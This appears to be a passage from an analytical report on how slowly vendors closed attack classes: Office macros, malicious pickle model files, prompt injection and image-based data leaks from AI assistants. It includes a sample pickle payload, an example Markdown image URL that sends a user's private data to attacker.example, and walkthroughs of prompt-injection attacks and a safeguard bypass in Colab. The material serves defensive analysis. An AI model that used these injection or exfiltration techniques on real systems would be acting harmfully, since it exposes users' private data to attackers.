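### Decades of warnings

Microsoft's main response was a warning. From version 7.0a, Word could ask users whether to open a document with its macros, without them or not at all. But Word couldn't tell a virus from a useful macro, and CIAC noted that many templates contained legitimate macros, so people who relied on them saw the warning constantly. Microsoft's *WD: Frequently Asked Questions About Word Macro Viruses* includes a question from a user who is tired of the warning, and the answer explains how to turn it off.

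The Melissa virus spread widely in March 1999 despite the warning. It arrived as a Word document attached to an email and, once its macro ran, mailed itself to fifty people in the victim's address book, according to Trend Micro's *20 Years of Macro Malware*. CERT/CC (1999) received the first confirmed reports on a Friday, and by Monday the virus had reached more than 100,000 computers. It could spread only through Word 97 and later versions, all of which had the warning, and the warning was on by default, according to Microsoft (1999). So on each infected machine, someone had clicked through the warning, or a person or an earlier virus had switched it off. Papa, a related virus, came with an email containing the instruction "Disregard macro warning."

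CERT/CC's advice that year was to "Disable macros by default". Microsoft did so for files from the internet 23 years later. A lull in attacks may explain part of the delay, since Trend Micro describes macro malware as nearly dormant from 2000 to 2005. But it returned in 2006. *Throwback Thursday* (Martin, 2016) reports that Microsoft gave Office 2016 an option to block macros when macro malware was rising again in 2016. Organisations could therefore have the protection six years before it became the default.

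### The block and its withdrawal

In February 2022, Microsoft announced that Office would by default block macros in files from the internet. The block relies on the *Mark of the Web*, a label that Windows attaches to browser downloads and email attachments. Office used to show a warning with an "Enable Content" button for these files. The new banner doesn't have that button, so anyone who wants to run the macros must open the file's properties and tick "Unblock".

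According to Microsoft's *Macros from the internet are blocked by default in Office*, the rollout began on 12 April 2022 with users of a preview version. On 7 July, the company withdrew the block from its main update channel "based on feedback", according to a notice quoted in BornCity's *Microsoft does not want to block macros in Office by default* (2022). A Microsoft manager quoted by Malwarebytes (2022) said the withdrawal was temporary and was meant to make the change easier to use. The rollout resumed on 27 July and reached the slowest business channel in January 2023.

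Microsoft said little about the complaints, but its instructions to administrators show some of the work involved. Companies had to find out which departments used macros, ask outside suppliers to sign theirs digitally, and decide which shared folders to trust. Microsoft reduced the disruption by still allowing macros that come from a trusted publisher or folder, or that the user had already enabled in that document. The block applies only to Office on Windows.

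Businesses' reliance on macros best explains the long delay. Users could already block macros, and CERT/CC had recommended doing so, yet when Microsoft finally changed the default, it had to reverse the change once. A macro that prepares a company's invoices is a program, as Melissa was, so a block that stops every attack also stops the invoices. Microsoft's eventual rule worked better because most attacks came from the internet, while many business macros came from inside the company.

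### Where the attackers went

The security company Proofpoint saw fewer email malware campaigns using VBA macros, the main kind in Office, once the change began. It counted just under 70 in October 2021 and just over 21 in June 2022, according to Computer Weekly. The October count was not unusually high, as Proofpoint's total for 2021 was almost 700, or about 58 a month, according to Cybersecurity Dive.

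Most of this fall came before the block reached most users, so attackers seem to have reacted to the announcement. A few large criminal groups can also shift the counts. In Proofpoint's *How Threat Actors Are Adapting to a Post-Macro World*, use of an older kind of Excel macro jumps in March 2022, probably because of a single group. But the decline lasted. In 2023, IBM saw 93% less spam with malicious VBA documents than the year before, and almost none after March.

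Attackers switched to other file types. From October 2021 to June 2022, Proofpoint recorded a rise of nearly 175% in campaigns using Windows shortcuts or *container files*, such as ISO and RAR, which hold other files. Windows put the Mark of the Web on a downloaded container but not on the document inside, so Office treated that document as local. A container could also hold a shortcut that launched the malware without a macro. In *Cyber Threat Actors Evading MOTW for Malware Delivery*, the Center for Internet Security, a non-profit with no product to sell based on the figure, reports a similar rise of 173% in cases involving container files from 2021 to 2022.

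Some groups then switched again, to files for Microsoft's note-taking program OneNote, as CrowdStrike's *QakBot eCrime Campaign Leverages Microsoft OneNote Attachments* describes. None of these counts measures how many computers attackers took over. The block nearly ended one class of attack, but users' safety improved less than the fall in macro campaigns suggests.

### How loading a model can run code

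An AI model consists mostly of *weights*, the numbers it learned in training. Developers often share models as files in *pickle*, the Python programming language's built-in format for saving data. A pickle file is a list of instructions for rebuilding the saved data, and these instructions can call almost any Python function.

Slaviero (2011), in *Sour Pickles*, includes this harmless example, which makes the computer wait ten seconds:

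| Text in the file | What Python does when it loads the file |
|---|---|
| `cos` and `system` | Finds `os.system`, a function that runs operating-system commands |
| `(S'sleep 10'` and `t` | Prepares `sleep 10` as the function's input |
| `R` | Calls the function |
| `.` | Stops |

An attacker can place such instructions in front of a real model's. The model still loads normally afterwards, so the victim may notice nothing.

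Slaviero presented this work at the Black Hat security conference on 4 August 2011, but did not claim to have discovered the problem. Python's documentation already warned prominently against loading pickles from untrusted sources, but there had been no practical guide to attacking them until his. PyTorch, now the main library for building AI models, was created later, so its developers chose pickle after the danger was public. Trail of Bits' *Never a dill moment* (2021) explained the risk for AI models and introduced Fickling, a tool for inspecting and creating malicious pickles.

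### A safer format and a safer default

In September 2022, Hugging Face, the largest site for sharing AI models, released *safetensors*, a format that stores weights and has no instruction for calling a function. Late that year, PyTorch 1.13 added a "weights-only" option, which allows only a short list of approved functions when loading a pickle. The option became the default in PyTorch 2.6, released in January 2025, though *PickleBall* (Kellas, Li and colleagues, 2025) dates the change to November 2024.

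In April 2025, PyTorch's maintainers disclosed CVE-2025-32434, a critical flaw that let a malicious file run code even with the option on. It affected versions up to 2.5.1, so users who had turned the option on in those versions were less safe than they thought. Version 2.6 already contained the fix.

The new default also blocks some harmless models. Kellas and colleagues examined 1,426 popular Hugging Face *repositories* (pages that each hold one or more model files) that offered only pickle models. In 219 of them (15.4%), at least one model needed a function that is not on PyTorch's approved list. Those 219 had 79.6 million downloads a month. Users can approve more functions, but they must work out which ones are safe. The makers of flair, a library for analysing text, instead turned the protection off in their own code so that their models would keep loading. People who use flair may therefore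 have the latest PyTorch without its safe default.

### How many models still use pickle

Kellas and colleagues measured how common pickle still is, as did Qin, Li and colleagues (2026), in *DITTO*, and their results are far apart:

| | Kellas and colleagues | Qin and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| Repositories studied | All with at least 1,000 monthly downloads in March 2025 | Those created from July 2025 to June 2026 with more than 1,000 monthly downloads |
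| Number | 16,661 | 10,023 |
| Share containing pickle models | 44.9% | 9.3% |

Kellas and colleagues counted popular repositories of any age, while Qin and colleagues counted only new ones, so the difference between their figures does not mean that pickle use fell by four fifths in a year. Old models stay popular for years, and publishers who convert a model to safetensors often keep the pickle version for users who still need it. Kellas and colleagues also identified pickle files by extension, whereas Qin and colleagues checked doubtful files and excluded 580 of 10,125, too few to explain the gap.

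The 44.9% figure better reflects what people were downloading in 2025, though the 9.3% is good news about new models. Even among the new repositories, one pickle model had 7.2 million downloads a month.

### How well scanners catch malicious models

People who must load a pickle without PyTorch's protection depend on *scanners*, programs that check a file for dangerous instructions before anyone loads it. Hugging Face runs several on the models it hosts. One, PickleScan, mainly checks which functions a file references.

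Qin and colleagues found that PickleScan flagged about a quarter of the harmless models in their test. These included 21 files chosen because Hugging Face had already labelled them "unsafe", all of which turned out to be harmless. Most of the 21 were image-recognition models that used a function attackers also use. Without them, the false-alarm rate was 23%. If one model in 1,000 were malicious, that rate would produce more than 200 false alarms for each real one, and users would soon learn to ignore them, as they did with Word's warning.

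Scanners also miss attacks. *DITTO* tested three scanners on seven malicious files packaged so that PyTorch or another library would find the pickle inside but a scanner might not. None of the scanners could scan any of the files. In *On the (In)Security of Loading Machine Learning Models* (2025), researchers uploaded the same malicious pickle to Hugging Face with different file extensions. PickleScan recognised it under some extensions and labelled it "not a pickle" under others. These tests used attacks designed to evade scanners, so they don't measure the share of real malicious models that scanners miss.

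Qin and colleagues built a scanner, also called DITTO, which simulates loading the file and asks a language model whether the instructions look like normal model loading. It caught all 92 malicious models in their benchmark and wrongly flagged 0.7% of the 959 harmless ones. The team also built the benchmark, so results on new attacks could be worse. The language model reads text that the attacker wrote, so the scanner could be vulnerable to prompt injection.

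### Two class lags

For both classes, the lag depends on what counts as protection.

| Attack class | Clock starts | Clock stops | Class lag |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office macros | Demonstration virus, December 1994 | Warning on by default, March 1999 at the latest | 4 years or less |
| Office macros | Demonstration virus, December 1994 | Block on by default, July 2022 to January 2023 | About 28 years |
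| Pickle models | *Sour Pickles*, August 2011 | Safe loading on by default in PyTorch, January 2025 | 13 years |
| Pickle models | *Never a dill moment*, March 2021 | Safe loading on by default in PyTorch, January 2025 | 4 years |
| Pickle models | *Sour Pickles*, August 2011 | Safe loading in most deployed systems | Not shown; possibly more than 15 years |

Melissa is a strong reason not to count the warning as protection, so the lag for macros is 28 years. Starting from the Lotus 1-2-3 discussions would add several more. For pickle, 2011 is the better starting date for the attack itself, but 2021 is fairer for measuring how fast PyTorch's developers reacted once someone had described the risk for AI models. The end date is uncertain because nobody has measured how many systems run PyTorch 2.6 or later without a library that turns the protection off.

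### The cost of breaking existing work

Compatibility seems to have delayed both protections, but it was a bigger obstacle for macros. A macro is useful because it runs commands, so blocking it removes what the user wanted. Most model files need only their weights, so Safetensors could drop the commands, and PyTorch could restrict them while still loading all the models in about 85% of the pickle-only repositories that Kellas and colleagues sampled.

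In these two cases, the default changed more slowly where attacks were worse. Macro viruses were the most common kind of virus in the late 1990s, yet Office's default took more than two decades to change. PyTorch changed its default even though malicious models have caused nothing on Melissa's scale. Researchers have found some on Hugging Face that steal passwords. With only two cases, other differences could matter just as much, such as the age of the software or how often its users update.

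Kellas and colleagues report that almost all malicious models on Hugging Face use pickle, and attackers have had little reason to switch so far. If pickle stopped working for them, attackers could use other formats. *An Empirical Study of Safetensors' Usage Trends and Developers' Perceptions* (2025) lists several that can run an attacker's code when a model is loaded, including H5, the older format of the Keras library.

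## Prompt injection, 2022 to 2026

Prompt injection became public in September 2022, and no vendor has found a complete fix. The attacker's command is ordinary text in material that the AI system has to read, so the approaches that worked for Office macros and model files don't work here. Office can block a macro because it can identify which part of a document is the macro, and safetensors made model files safer by leaving out commands.

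### From a translation trick to an attack class

On 11 September 2022, Riley Goodside posted examples of an attack on GPT-3, an OpenAI language model. Goodside asked it to translate text into French, but the text contained instructions to ignore that request and write a joke phrase instead. GPT-3 wrote the phrase, even when the request included a warning that the text might contain tricks. The next day, Willison (2022) named the attack "prompt injection" in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* and pointed out that companies were already building products on GPT-3.

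The first defences failed almost at once. One put the untrusted text in quotation marks within a fixed format, but someone soon wrote a text that got around it. Another asked the model to check for injections, but an attacker could add a line telling it to report that there were none. Twitter users made a recruitment startup's bot reveal its instructions and threaten to overthrow the US president. On 16 September, Willison (2022) wrote in *I don’t know how to solve prompt injection* that he knew how to prevent SQL injection and cross-site scripting but had no reliable way to prevent prompt injection.

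In these early cases, the attacker typed the text into the system directly. In *indirect* prompt injection, the attacker hides instructions in a web page, email or document for an AI system to read. Researchers demonstrated this in early 2023, when chatbots were starting to search the web. A job applicant could hide a line in a CV telling the employer's AI system to approve the application. The indirect form is more dangerous for agents because the victim is a user who has done nothing wrong and may never see the text.

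### One stream of text

An early translation service might have built its request to the model in much the same way as the school website built its database query:

`"Translate the following text into French: " + text`

Willison hoped for a GPT-3 equivalent of parameterised queries, with one field for instructions and others for data. One version of GPT-3 already had separate fields, but it still followed instructions placed in the data field. By April 2023, he thought the idea would be extremely difficult, if not impossible, to implement with existing language models.

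Separate fields don't help because the model processes all its input as one sequence of *tokens*, short pieces of text, and calculates which token is likely to come next. Developers of newer chat models mark which text came from the user and which from a web page, but these marks are also tokens in the sequence. A database separates commands from values by a rule in its code that holds for every input, whereas a model learns in training to give some parts of its input more authority than others, and what it has learned can fail on text unlike its training examples.

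Complete separation would also make agents less useful. A programmer may want an agent to follow the installation steps on a web page, and those steps are instructions inside untrusted data. The agent has to judge which instructions serve the user's purpose, and an attacker can try to mislead it.

### Two predictions that it will never be solved

On 8 December 2025, the UK's National Cyber Security Centre published *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* by David C, its technical director for platforms research. He wrote that prompt injection may never be fully mitigated in the way that SQL injection can be, and warned that developers who treat the two as alike will look for a fix that doesn't exist.

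He prefers to compare language models to a *confused deputy*, a program tricked into using its privileges for someone who lacks them. Developers can repair an ordinary confused deputy, but he calls language models "inherently confusable". Developers should therefore assume that some attacks will succeed and limit the damage. If a system can't tolerate the remaining risk, a language model may be the wrong tool for it.

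David C fears that prompt injection will repeat the history of SQL injection. He says SQL injection attacks peaked around 2010, after websites had come to depend on databases without protecting them, and became rare only after a decade of breaches. That may be too optimistic, since CISA and MITRE still record SQL injection flaws. Unlike SQL injection, whose complete fix took decades to spread, prompt injection has no complete fix.

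Two weeks later, OpenAI reached a similar conclusion about Atlas, its web browser with a built-in agent that can click and type for the user. *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) compares prompt injection to scams and says it is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". OpenAI had a commercial reason to sound more confident, so the admission is somewhat more credible, though it also lowers expectations of what the company must achieve.

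Both statements rule out guaranteed protection but allow that the risk could be greatly reduced. To reduce it, the NCSC puts more trust in ordinary software that restricts what the model can do, while OpenAI emphasises finding new attacks quickly and training the model to resist them.

### Training the model to resist

OpenAI began selling models trained to rank the developer's instructions above text from other sources in July 2024, with GPT-4o mini. It also trained a language model to attack the agent in its Atlas browser. The attacking model repeatedly tests an injection in a simulation and revises it using a record of the agent's full reasoning and actions. In one attack it found, an email in the user's inbox caused the agent to send a resignation letter to the user's chief executive when the user had asked for an out-of-office reply.

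OpenAI then trained the agent against such attacks and released the new version to all Atlas users by December 2025. Because OpenAI hosts the model, installation added almost no delay. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (July 2026) introduced a stronger automated attacker and reported that the company's latest models already scored too high on the commonly used robustness tests for those tests to measure further improvement.

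Training a model to resist prompt injection requires no action from the user. The likely drawback is that a model trained too hard to ignore instructions in documents may also ignore ones the user wants it to follow, such as those in a project's style guide.

### Filters and monitors

A filter inspects text before the model acts on it, and a monitor inspects the action the model is about to take. Microsoft began offering its filter, Prompt Shields, to developers in 2024. Anthropic uses both in its agents. The filter checks tool outputs for injected instructions, and the monitor blocks actions that seem dangerous. The combination, called auto mode, is now the default in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent.

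David C warns against filters that look for known phrases, because an attacker can word the same instruction in endless ways. Filters also interrupt legitimate work when they flag harmless pages. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya, Zhang and colleagues (2026) searched 1.2 billion web addresses and confirmed injections on 9,676 pages, or about 8 in every million. If a filter wrongly flagged 0.1% of harmless pages, it would raise about 1,000 false alarms for every 8 real injections. Vendors therefore have to keep false alarms extremely rare or let some attacks through.

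### Limiting what the agent can do

The third kind of mitigation assumes that the model will sometimes obey an attacker, and restricts what it can do as a result. David C cites a rule from a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista that when a model reads text from someone, its privileges should drop to that person's. An agent reading email from a stranger would then have no access to tools the stranger shouldn't use.

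CaMeL, a design that researchers at Google and ETH Zurich published in 2025, applies this idea more precisely. Suppose a user asks an agent to find Ben's new address in his latest email and send it to Anna.

1. One language model sees only the user's request. It writes a short program that fetches the email, extracts the address and sends it to Anna.
2. A second model reads the email and extracts the address. It has no tools.
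3. Ordinary software runs the program, keeps track of which values came from the email, and checks each action against rules that someone wrote in advance.

CaMeL is the closest equivalent to a parameterised query so far, because it separates commands from data in the software around the model. An instruction hidden in an email can make the model that reads it return a false address, but it can't add a step that forwards the user's files to a stranger. CaMeL doesn't protect the accuracy of what the agent reports, so an injection can still distort a summary.

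In its developers' tests, an agent using CaMeL completed 77% of tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended one. The loss would be greater for open-ended work. If the user asks the agent to do whatever Ben's email requests, the first model can't write the program without knowing what the email contains. Someone must also write the rules, and an overly loose rule lets attacks through. Microsoft has developed a related design called FIDES, according to PYMNTS's *Anthropic Pushes Back as Hackers Press AI Weak Spots*.

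The limits that have reached consumer products are simpler. According to Fortune (2025), Atlas already had a logged-out mode in October 2025, which let the agent browse without the user's accounts, and a Watch Mode, which kept the user involved on sensitive sites. Atlas also asks for confirmation before it sends an email or completes a purchase. A logged-out agent can't sort the user's inbox, though, and people who confirm dozens of harmless actions may stop reading the requests, as many Word users did with the macro warning.

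### Success rates in late 2026

The most detailed current figures are in Anthropic's September 2026 system card (a developer's report on its tests of a new model) for Claude Fable 5.1. The security firm Gray Swan ran the first test below and built the attacking software for all the others except the browser test.

| Task | How the attacks were prepared | Attempts per scenario | Success per attempt | At least one success | At least one success, with injection filters |
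|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Mixed, 37 scenarios | Fixed set from public competitions | 15 | 0.1% | 1.0% | Not reported |
| Browsing | Written against an older model | 10 | 2.64% | 10 of 110 scenarios | 0 of 110 |
| Using a computer's screen and mouse | Optimised on the test scenarios | 200 | 0.07% | 2 of 14 | 2 of 14 |
| Coding, earlier attacker | Optimised on the test scenarios | 200 | 9.26% | 31 of 40 | 18 of 40 |
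| Coding, newer attacker | Optimised further, on more varied attacks | 200 | 56.87% | 38 of 40 | 36 of 40 |

Results for the same model range from almost no successful attacks to success in nearly every scenario, and much of the difference comes from the attacker. On the same 40 scenarios, the earlier coding attacker succeeded in 2.68% of its attempts against Claude Opus 5, another Anthropic model, while the newer one succeeded in 90.93%. A low success rate for one attacker is therefore weak evidence of how the model will do against a better one.

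Anthropic considers the coding tests deliberately generous to the attacker, because a real attacker usually can't practise on the exact system they want to attack, and 200 attempts would give defenders many chances to notice. This reasoning is fair for an attack on one company, but an attacker can buy access to the same model, build a similar agent and practise on it unobserved, so the tests may be less generous than Anthropic implies.

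Fable 5.1's coding results reflect the behavior of two models. A separate filter, meant to stop people using Fable 5.1 for hacking, passes suspicious requests to an older model, Claude Opus 4.8. In the test with the newer attacker, about 64% of requests went to Opus 4.8, and every successful attack was among them. No attack succeeded in the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself. This may overstate Fable 5.1's own resistance, because the filter could have passed the most effective attacks to Opus 4.8. The distinction hardly matters to users, since the product includes both models.

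No attacks succeeded in the browser test's 110 scenarios. This is a good result, but attackers could still break up to about 2.7% of similar scenarios, at 95% confidence. The result is also limited because the attacks had worked on an older model and were not adapted to the new filters.

OpenAI's figures are averages over its own tests. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* gives August 2026 success rates against GPT-5.6 Sol of about 0.05% for direct attacks and 3.77% for indirect ones. Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, reports October figures for GPT-6 Sol that imply rates of 0.01% and 2.87%. If the two sets of tests are comparable, OpenAI cut the success rate of direct attacks by about four fifths, but that of indirect attacks, which matter more for agents, by only about a quarter.

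Other companies' models did worse than Anthropic's on Gray Swan's fixed set of attacks. After 15 attempts, the attacks had succeeded 9.2% of the time against Gemini 3.7 Flash, the most resistant of them, and between 24% and 53% of the time against most of the rest. PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* reports successful attacks on leading models from every provider during long office tasks, such as analysing a bond portfolio. PromptArmor sells security services, so it benefits from such findings, but its results are a useful check on tests that developers run or commission.

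### Injections in the wild

Attacks that people have placed on websites work much less often. Khodayari and colleagues collected 15,387 injections, most of them from web pages archived in October 2025, and tried 100 of them on 13 language models. They gave each model the page in four formats, asked for a summary and checked whether it followed the injected instruction instead.

| Models | Trials | Injection worked |
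|---|---|---|
| Small, open | 1,200 | 4.2% |
| Medium, open | 2,000 | 0.6% |
| Large, open | 1,200 | 1.2% |
| Closed, such as GPT models | 800 | 0.6% |

The page's format affected the success rate of injections as much as the choice of model did. Injections worked in 3.9% of trials when the researchers reduced the page to plain text and in 1.1% when they kept its HTML code, probably because the code reveals that the instruction was hidden. About a fifth of the HTML trials ended in errors, mainly because the page was too long for the model, so some of the low rates are misleading. In six trials, a model's output identified the injection and warned about it, but the model still followed it.

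Few of these injections look like the work of skilled thieves. The sites' own operators wrote about 80% of those on the archived pages. Many were meant to stop AI companies from using the sites' content or to expose automated visitors, for example by telling any AI system to return random numbers. Others were meant to improve the reputation of a product or person. 54 templates accounted for 95% of the injections. Nearly all used a blunt command to drop the current task, which developers have been training models to ignore since 2022.

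The researchers could find only injections that contained one of 3,963 known phrases, so they would have missed a subtle attack written for one target. They also tested summarization, not agents with tools. The 0.6% to 4.2% range is therefore a reasonable estimate of how often today's common injections work on a model that reads the web, but a poor estimate of how often a determined attacker could succeed. A growing share of injections may also be malicious. Khodayari and colleagues cite a Google analysis in which malicious injections on the web rose by 32% between November 2025 and February 2026.

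### How low is low enough?

Any fall in the success rate is a mitigation as defined earlier, but an attacker can often try again. If attempts are independent and each succeeds with probability p, the probability of at least one success in n attempts is 1 − (1 − p)^n. At 1% per attempt, an attacker who tries 100 times has about a 63% chance of succeeding at least once.

| Success per attempt | 10 attempts | 100 attempts | 1,000 attempts |
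|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 9.6% | 63% | Over 99.9% |
| 0.1% | 1.0% | 9.5% | 63% |
| 0.01% | 0.1% | 1.0% | 9.5% |

A tenfold improvement in the model is cancelled if the attacker makes ten times as many attempts, and sending more emails costs almost nothing.

Real attempts are not independent, however. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that Gray Swan's attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with 100. If the attempts had been independent, the rate would have been 38% with ten and 99% with 100. Some scenarios were harder to break than others, and repeated failures suggest that a scenario is one of the hard ones. The gap is larger in Fable 5.1's coding results with filters, where 200 independent attempts at 2.05% each would have broken about 98% of the scenarios, but the attacker broke 45%.

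The formula therefore tends to overstate the danger to one well-protected target. It is less relevant to an attacker who doesn't care which user is compromised. Someone who sends the same email to 1,000 people can expect ten successes at an average rate of 1%, whether or not the attempts are independent. Independence affects only how much the actual number varies around ten. If the agents all run the same model in the same way, the email might fail everywhere or succeed in hundreds of inboxes at once.

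The acceptable success rate for attacks depends on what the agent can do. A 1% chance of a false sentence in a summary may be tolerable, but the same chance that an agent sends money to a stranger is not. This is a reason to limit the agent's actions, which reduces the damage from a successful attack even if the success rate stays the same.

### Is the class closing?

The argument that developers are gradually fixing this class of flaw relies on how fast attack success rates have fallen. VentureBeat reported in February 2026 that attackers with 200 attempts succeeded in 78.6% of scenarios against Claude Opus 4.6, or 57.1% with safeguards, consistent with 11 and 8 of 14 scenarios. Seven months later, attackers succeeded in 2 of 14 scenarios against Fable 5.1 using a computer, with or without filters. The comparison assumes that the scenarios and the attacker stayed similar.

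Browser agents also became more resistant to prompt injection. VentureBeat reports that in May 2026, attacks on Claude Opus 4.8's browser agent succeeded 31.5% of the time without safeguards and 0.5% with them. For Opus 5, the rate fell to zero across 129 scenarios, and The Decoder titled its article *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. Vendors of hosted agents can also deliver each improvement to all their users at once, which the makers of C compilers and web frameworks could never do.

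But some of this progress disappears when the test changes. The same article reports an attack success rate of 2.0% against Opus 5 after 15 attempts on Gray Swan's fixed set. In September, after the set had gained nine scenarios and 670 attacks, the rate was 4.8%. The later test also included fallbacks to older models, though Anthropic found that these made little difference on this set. Without safeguards, at least one attack on Opus 5 succeeded in 7 of the 110 new browser scenarios.

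Attackers found new ways around stack canaries and non-executable memory for years, and prompt injection seems to be following that pattern faster. Those protections blocked particular techniques completely, but training a model against an attack only makes the attack less likely to succeed, so an attacker may not need a new technique.

Hosting also gives users only partial protection. Anthropic can replace Fable 5.1 for everyone in a day, but a product running on it routed many coding requests to an older, weaker model. Companies that self-host small open models have to install improvements themselves, and those models were the most vulnerable to injections in the wild.

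A few leading vendors appear to have made known attacks rare in browsing and computer use, while coding agents and most other models still seem exposed to a capable attacker. This does not amount to protection by default in most deployed systems, even under the looser definition that put the end of the buffer overflow lag around 2008. The class lag is therefore censored at more than four years, counting from Goodside's examples, or nearly four, counting from the first indirect attacks. If the NCSC and OpenAI are right, the lag would remain censored permanently under a definition that requires prompt injection to disappear.

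## The same leak at many AI vendors

Vendors can't yet fully prevent prompt injection, but they can fix individual flaws that make it harmful. In one such flaw, an injection makes an assistant display an image whose web address carries the user's private data to an attacker. Researchers have reported this flaw often, in products from at least ten vendors since 2023, so the reports are unusually good evidence of how fast AI vendors fix flaws. A second flaw, Whisper Leak, reveals the topic of an encrypted chat. Microsoft's researchers reported it to 28 providers at about the same time.

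### How an image leaks a conversation

Assistants usually format their replies in Markdown, a notation in which `![caption](address)` displays an image. The user's browser requests the image from the server at that address, and the server can record the whole address, including any text at the end.

Suppose a user has told an assistant about Ben's diabetes and then asks it to summarise a web page. The page contains a hidden instruction to add whatever the user has said to an image address. If the assistant obeys, its reply includes this:

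`![logo](https://attacker.example/logo.png?q=Ben+has+diabetes)`

The browser requests the image as soon as the reply appears, without any click, and the attacker reads the data in the server's log.

Johann Rehberger, an independent security researcher, demonstrated this against Microsoft's Bing Chat in 2023. In *Bing Chat*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red, he describes how text on a web page made the assistant wait for two more turns of conversation and then send him an encoded summary of the page and the chat. An attacker could have put such text in a comment or an advertisement on the page.

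The leak requires private data, text from a stranger and a way to send data out. Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta". In *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, a running list of such leaks up to July 2026, he argues that the way to send data out is generally the easiest of the three to remove.

Microsoft did this in Bing Chat, apparently with a Content Security Policy that allowed images from only four Microsoft addresses. An injection could still make the assistant write the image code, but the browser would not request the image.

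Other vendors blocked the request in other ways. Anthropic made users click "Show Image" first (Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*). In the Azure AI Playground, a tool for developers, Microsoft broke the image notation by inserting a space (Embrace The Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*). Google stopped displaying images and links in Vertex AI Studio, a similar tool (Embrace The Red's *Google Cloud Vertex AI*).

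All of these fixes are in ordinary software outside the model, so they work however persuasive the injection is. Google's developers had also instructed the assistant in Colab, Google's programming notebook, not to display images. Embrace The Red's *Google Colab AI* (2024) shows how Rehberger got around this by asking the assistant to join fragments of an image address.

### Thirteen reports

The table lists thirteen reports of this kind of leak, ordered by fix time. Where only a month is known, the range covers every possible date.

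| Product | Reported | Fixed | Fix time in days |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude | 12 July 2023 | 26 July 2023 | 14 |
| Google Bard | 19 September 2023 | By 19 October 2023 | 30 at most |
| Vertex AI Studio | 30 August 2023 | By 19 October 2023 | 50 at most |
| Azure AI Playground | 24 July 2023 | 13 September 2023 | 51 |
| Google Colab | 29 November 2023 | January 2024 | 33–63 |
| Bing Chat | 8 April 2023 | 15 June 2023 | 68 |
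| GitHub Copilot Chat (CamoLeak) | June 2025 at the earliest | By 14 August 2025 | 74 at most |
| GitHub Copilot Chat (first report) | 25 February 2024 | 12 June 2024 | 108 |
| Google NotebookLM | 4 December 2023 | By 19 April 2024 | 132–137 |
| Microsoft 365 Copilot (EchoLeak) | January 2025 | May 2025 | 90–150 |
| ChatGPT | Early April 2023 | December 2023, partly | About 235–275 |
| xAI's Grok | By December 2024 | Refused | More than 14 |
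| Google Antigravity | By November 2025 | Refused | Unknown, still open |

Several of the dates are only upper bounds. Google told Rehberger about the Vertex fix when he asked, and he thinks the company had made it a few weeks earlier.

ChatGPT is the hardest case to classify. OpenAI first marked the report "won't fix", and Rehberger spent the next eight months publishing demonstrations while the company added features that made the leak more dangerous. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* reports that in December, ChatGPT's website began checking each image address with an OpenAI server before displaying the image. However, 9 of the 36 letters and digits Rehberger tried still got through as separate images, so an attacker could slowly spell out short messages. The iPhone app had no check at all. Fixes to hosted products usually reach users almost instantly,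 but OpenAI had put this check in code that runs on the user's device, so every app needed its own version.

The curve also depends on how the two refusals are treated. If they are censored on the last day anyone is known to have been waiting, they drop out of the Kaplan–Meier calculation within about two weeks. This assumes that xAI and Google would later fix their flaws as fast as other vendors did, which is optimistic because both had just refused. The last column of the next table instead treats both flaws as open throughout. Both columns use the latest possible date for each fix.

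| Days since report | Fixed so far | Still open, refusals censored early | Still open, refusals never fixed |
|---|---|---|---|
| 30 | 2 | 83% | 85% |
| 60 | 4 | 64% | 69% |
| 90 | 7 | 37% | 46% |
| 120 | 8 | 28% | 38% |
| 150 | 10 | 9% | 23% |
| 275 | 11 | 0% | 15% |

The half-life is 68 days if the refusals are censored early and 74 if they stay open. With the earliest plausible fix dates, it is 51 or 68 days. The refusals therefore have little effect on the middle of the curve but almost entirely determine its end. Not counting OpenAI's partial mitigation as a fix adds another 8 percentage points to the final figure in the last column.

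The curve can't show whether vendors have become faster, because the cases from 2026 lack report dates. Superhuman, which makes an email program, fixed the leak in January, but Willison doesn't say when it was reported. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026), which describes another leak in Microsoft 365 Copilot, doesn't give a report date either. Microsoft patched that leak in early June, before Varonis published it on 15 June, according to Daily Security Review's *CVE-2026-42824*.

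### Whose reports get counted

Rehberger made ten of the thirteen reports, so the table mostly shows how vendors respond to him. He tested well-known products, supplied working demonstrations and kept asking about progress, and a less persistent researcher might have waited much longer for fixes. Google confirmed the Bard fix after he asked whether he could show the attack at a conference. NotebookLM was still leaking 132 days after his report, when he published *Bobby Tables but with LLM Apps* on Embrace The Red. Google deployed a fix within five days of publication.

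Researchers also choose which cases to write about. A fix gives them a reason to publish, whereas a report that a vendor has been considering for six months may never become public. This makes the recorded fix times too short. Refusals may have the opposite effect, since they are newsworthy and could be overrepresented. On balance, the half-life is probably too low, because the missing cases are likely to include slow vendors and small products that nobody tested.

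The flaws also differed in severity. Rehberger rated those in Vertex and the Azure playground as medium because neither product could yet fetch outside content, so a victim would have had to paste in the malicious text. He reported the Colab flaw before it was serious, expecting Google to add the notebook's contents to the prompt, and Google later did.

### The next product has the same flaw

Google received reports of this leak in four of its products in just over three months in 2023. According to Singh of the bug-bounty company HackerOne, researchers demonstrated it in Bard less than 24 hours after Google launched Extensions, which let the assistant read a user's email and documents. Google responded inconsistently. It accepted the Vertex report after 22 minutes, fixed Colab without paying a reward and left NotebookLM vulnerable until the flaw was public.

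In November 2025, two years after Google fixed Bard, a researcher found that the company's new coding tool, Antigravity, also leaked data through images. Google classed the report as "intended behavior". Its page for bug hunters listed data leaks in Antigravity as a known problem the company was working on, so it paid no rewards for reporting them.

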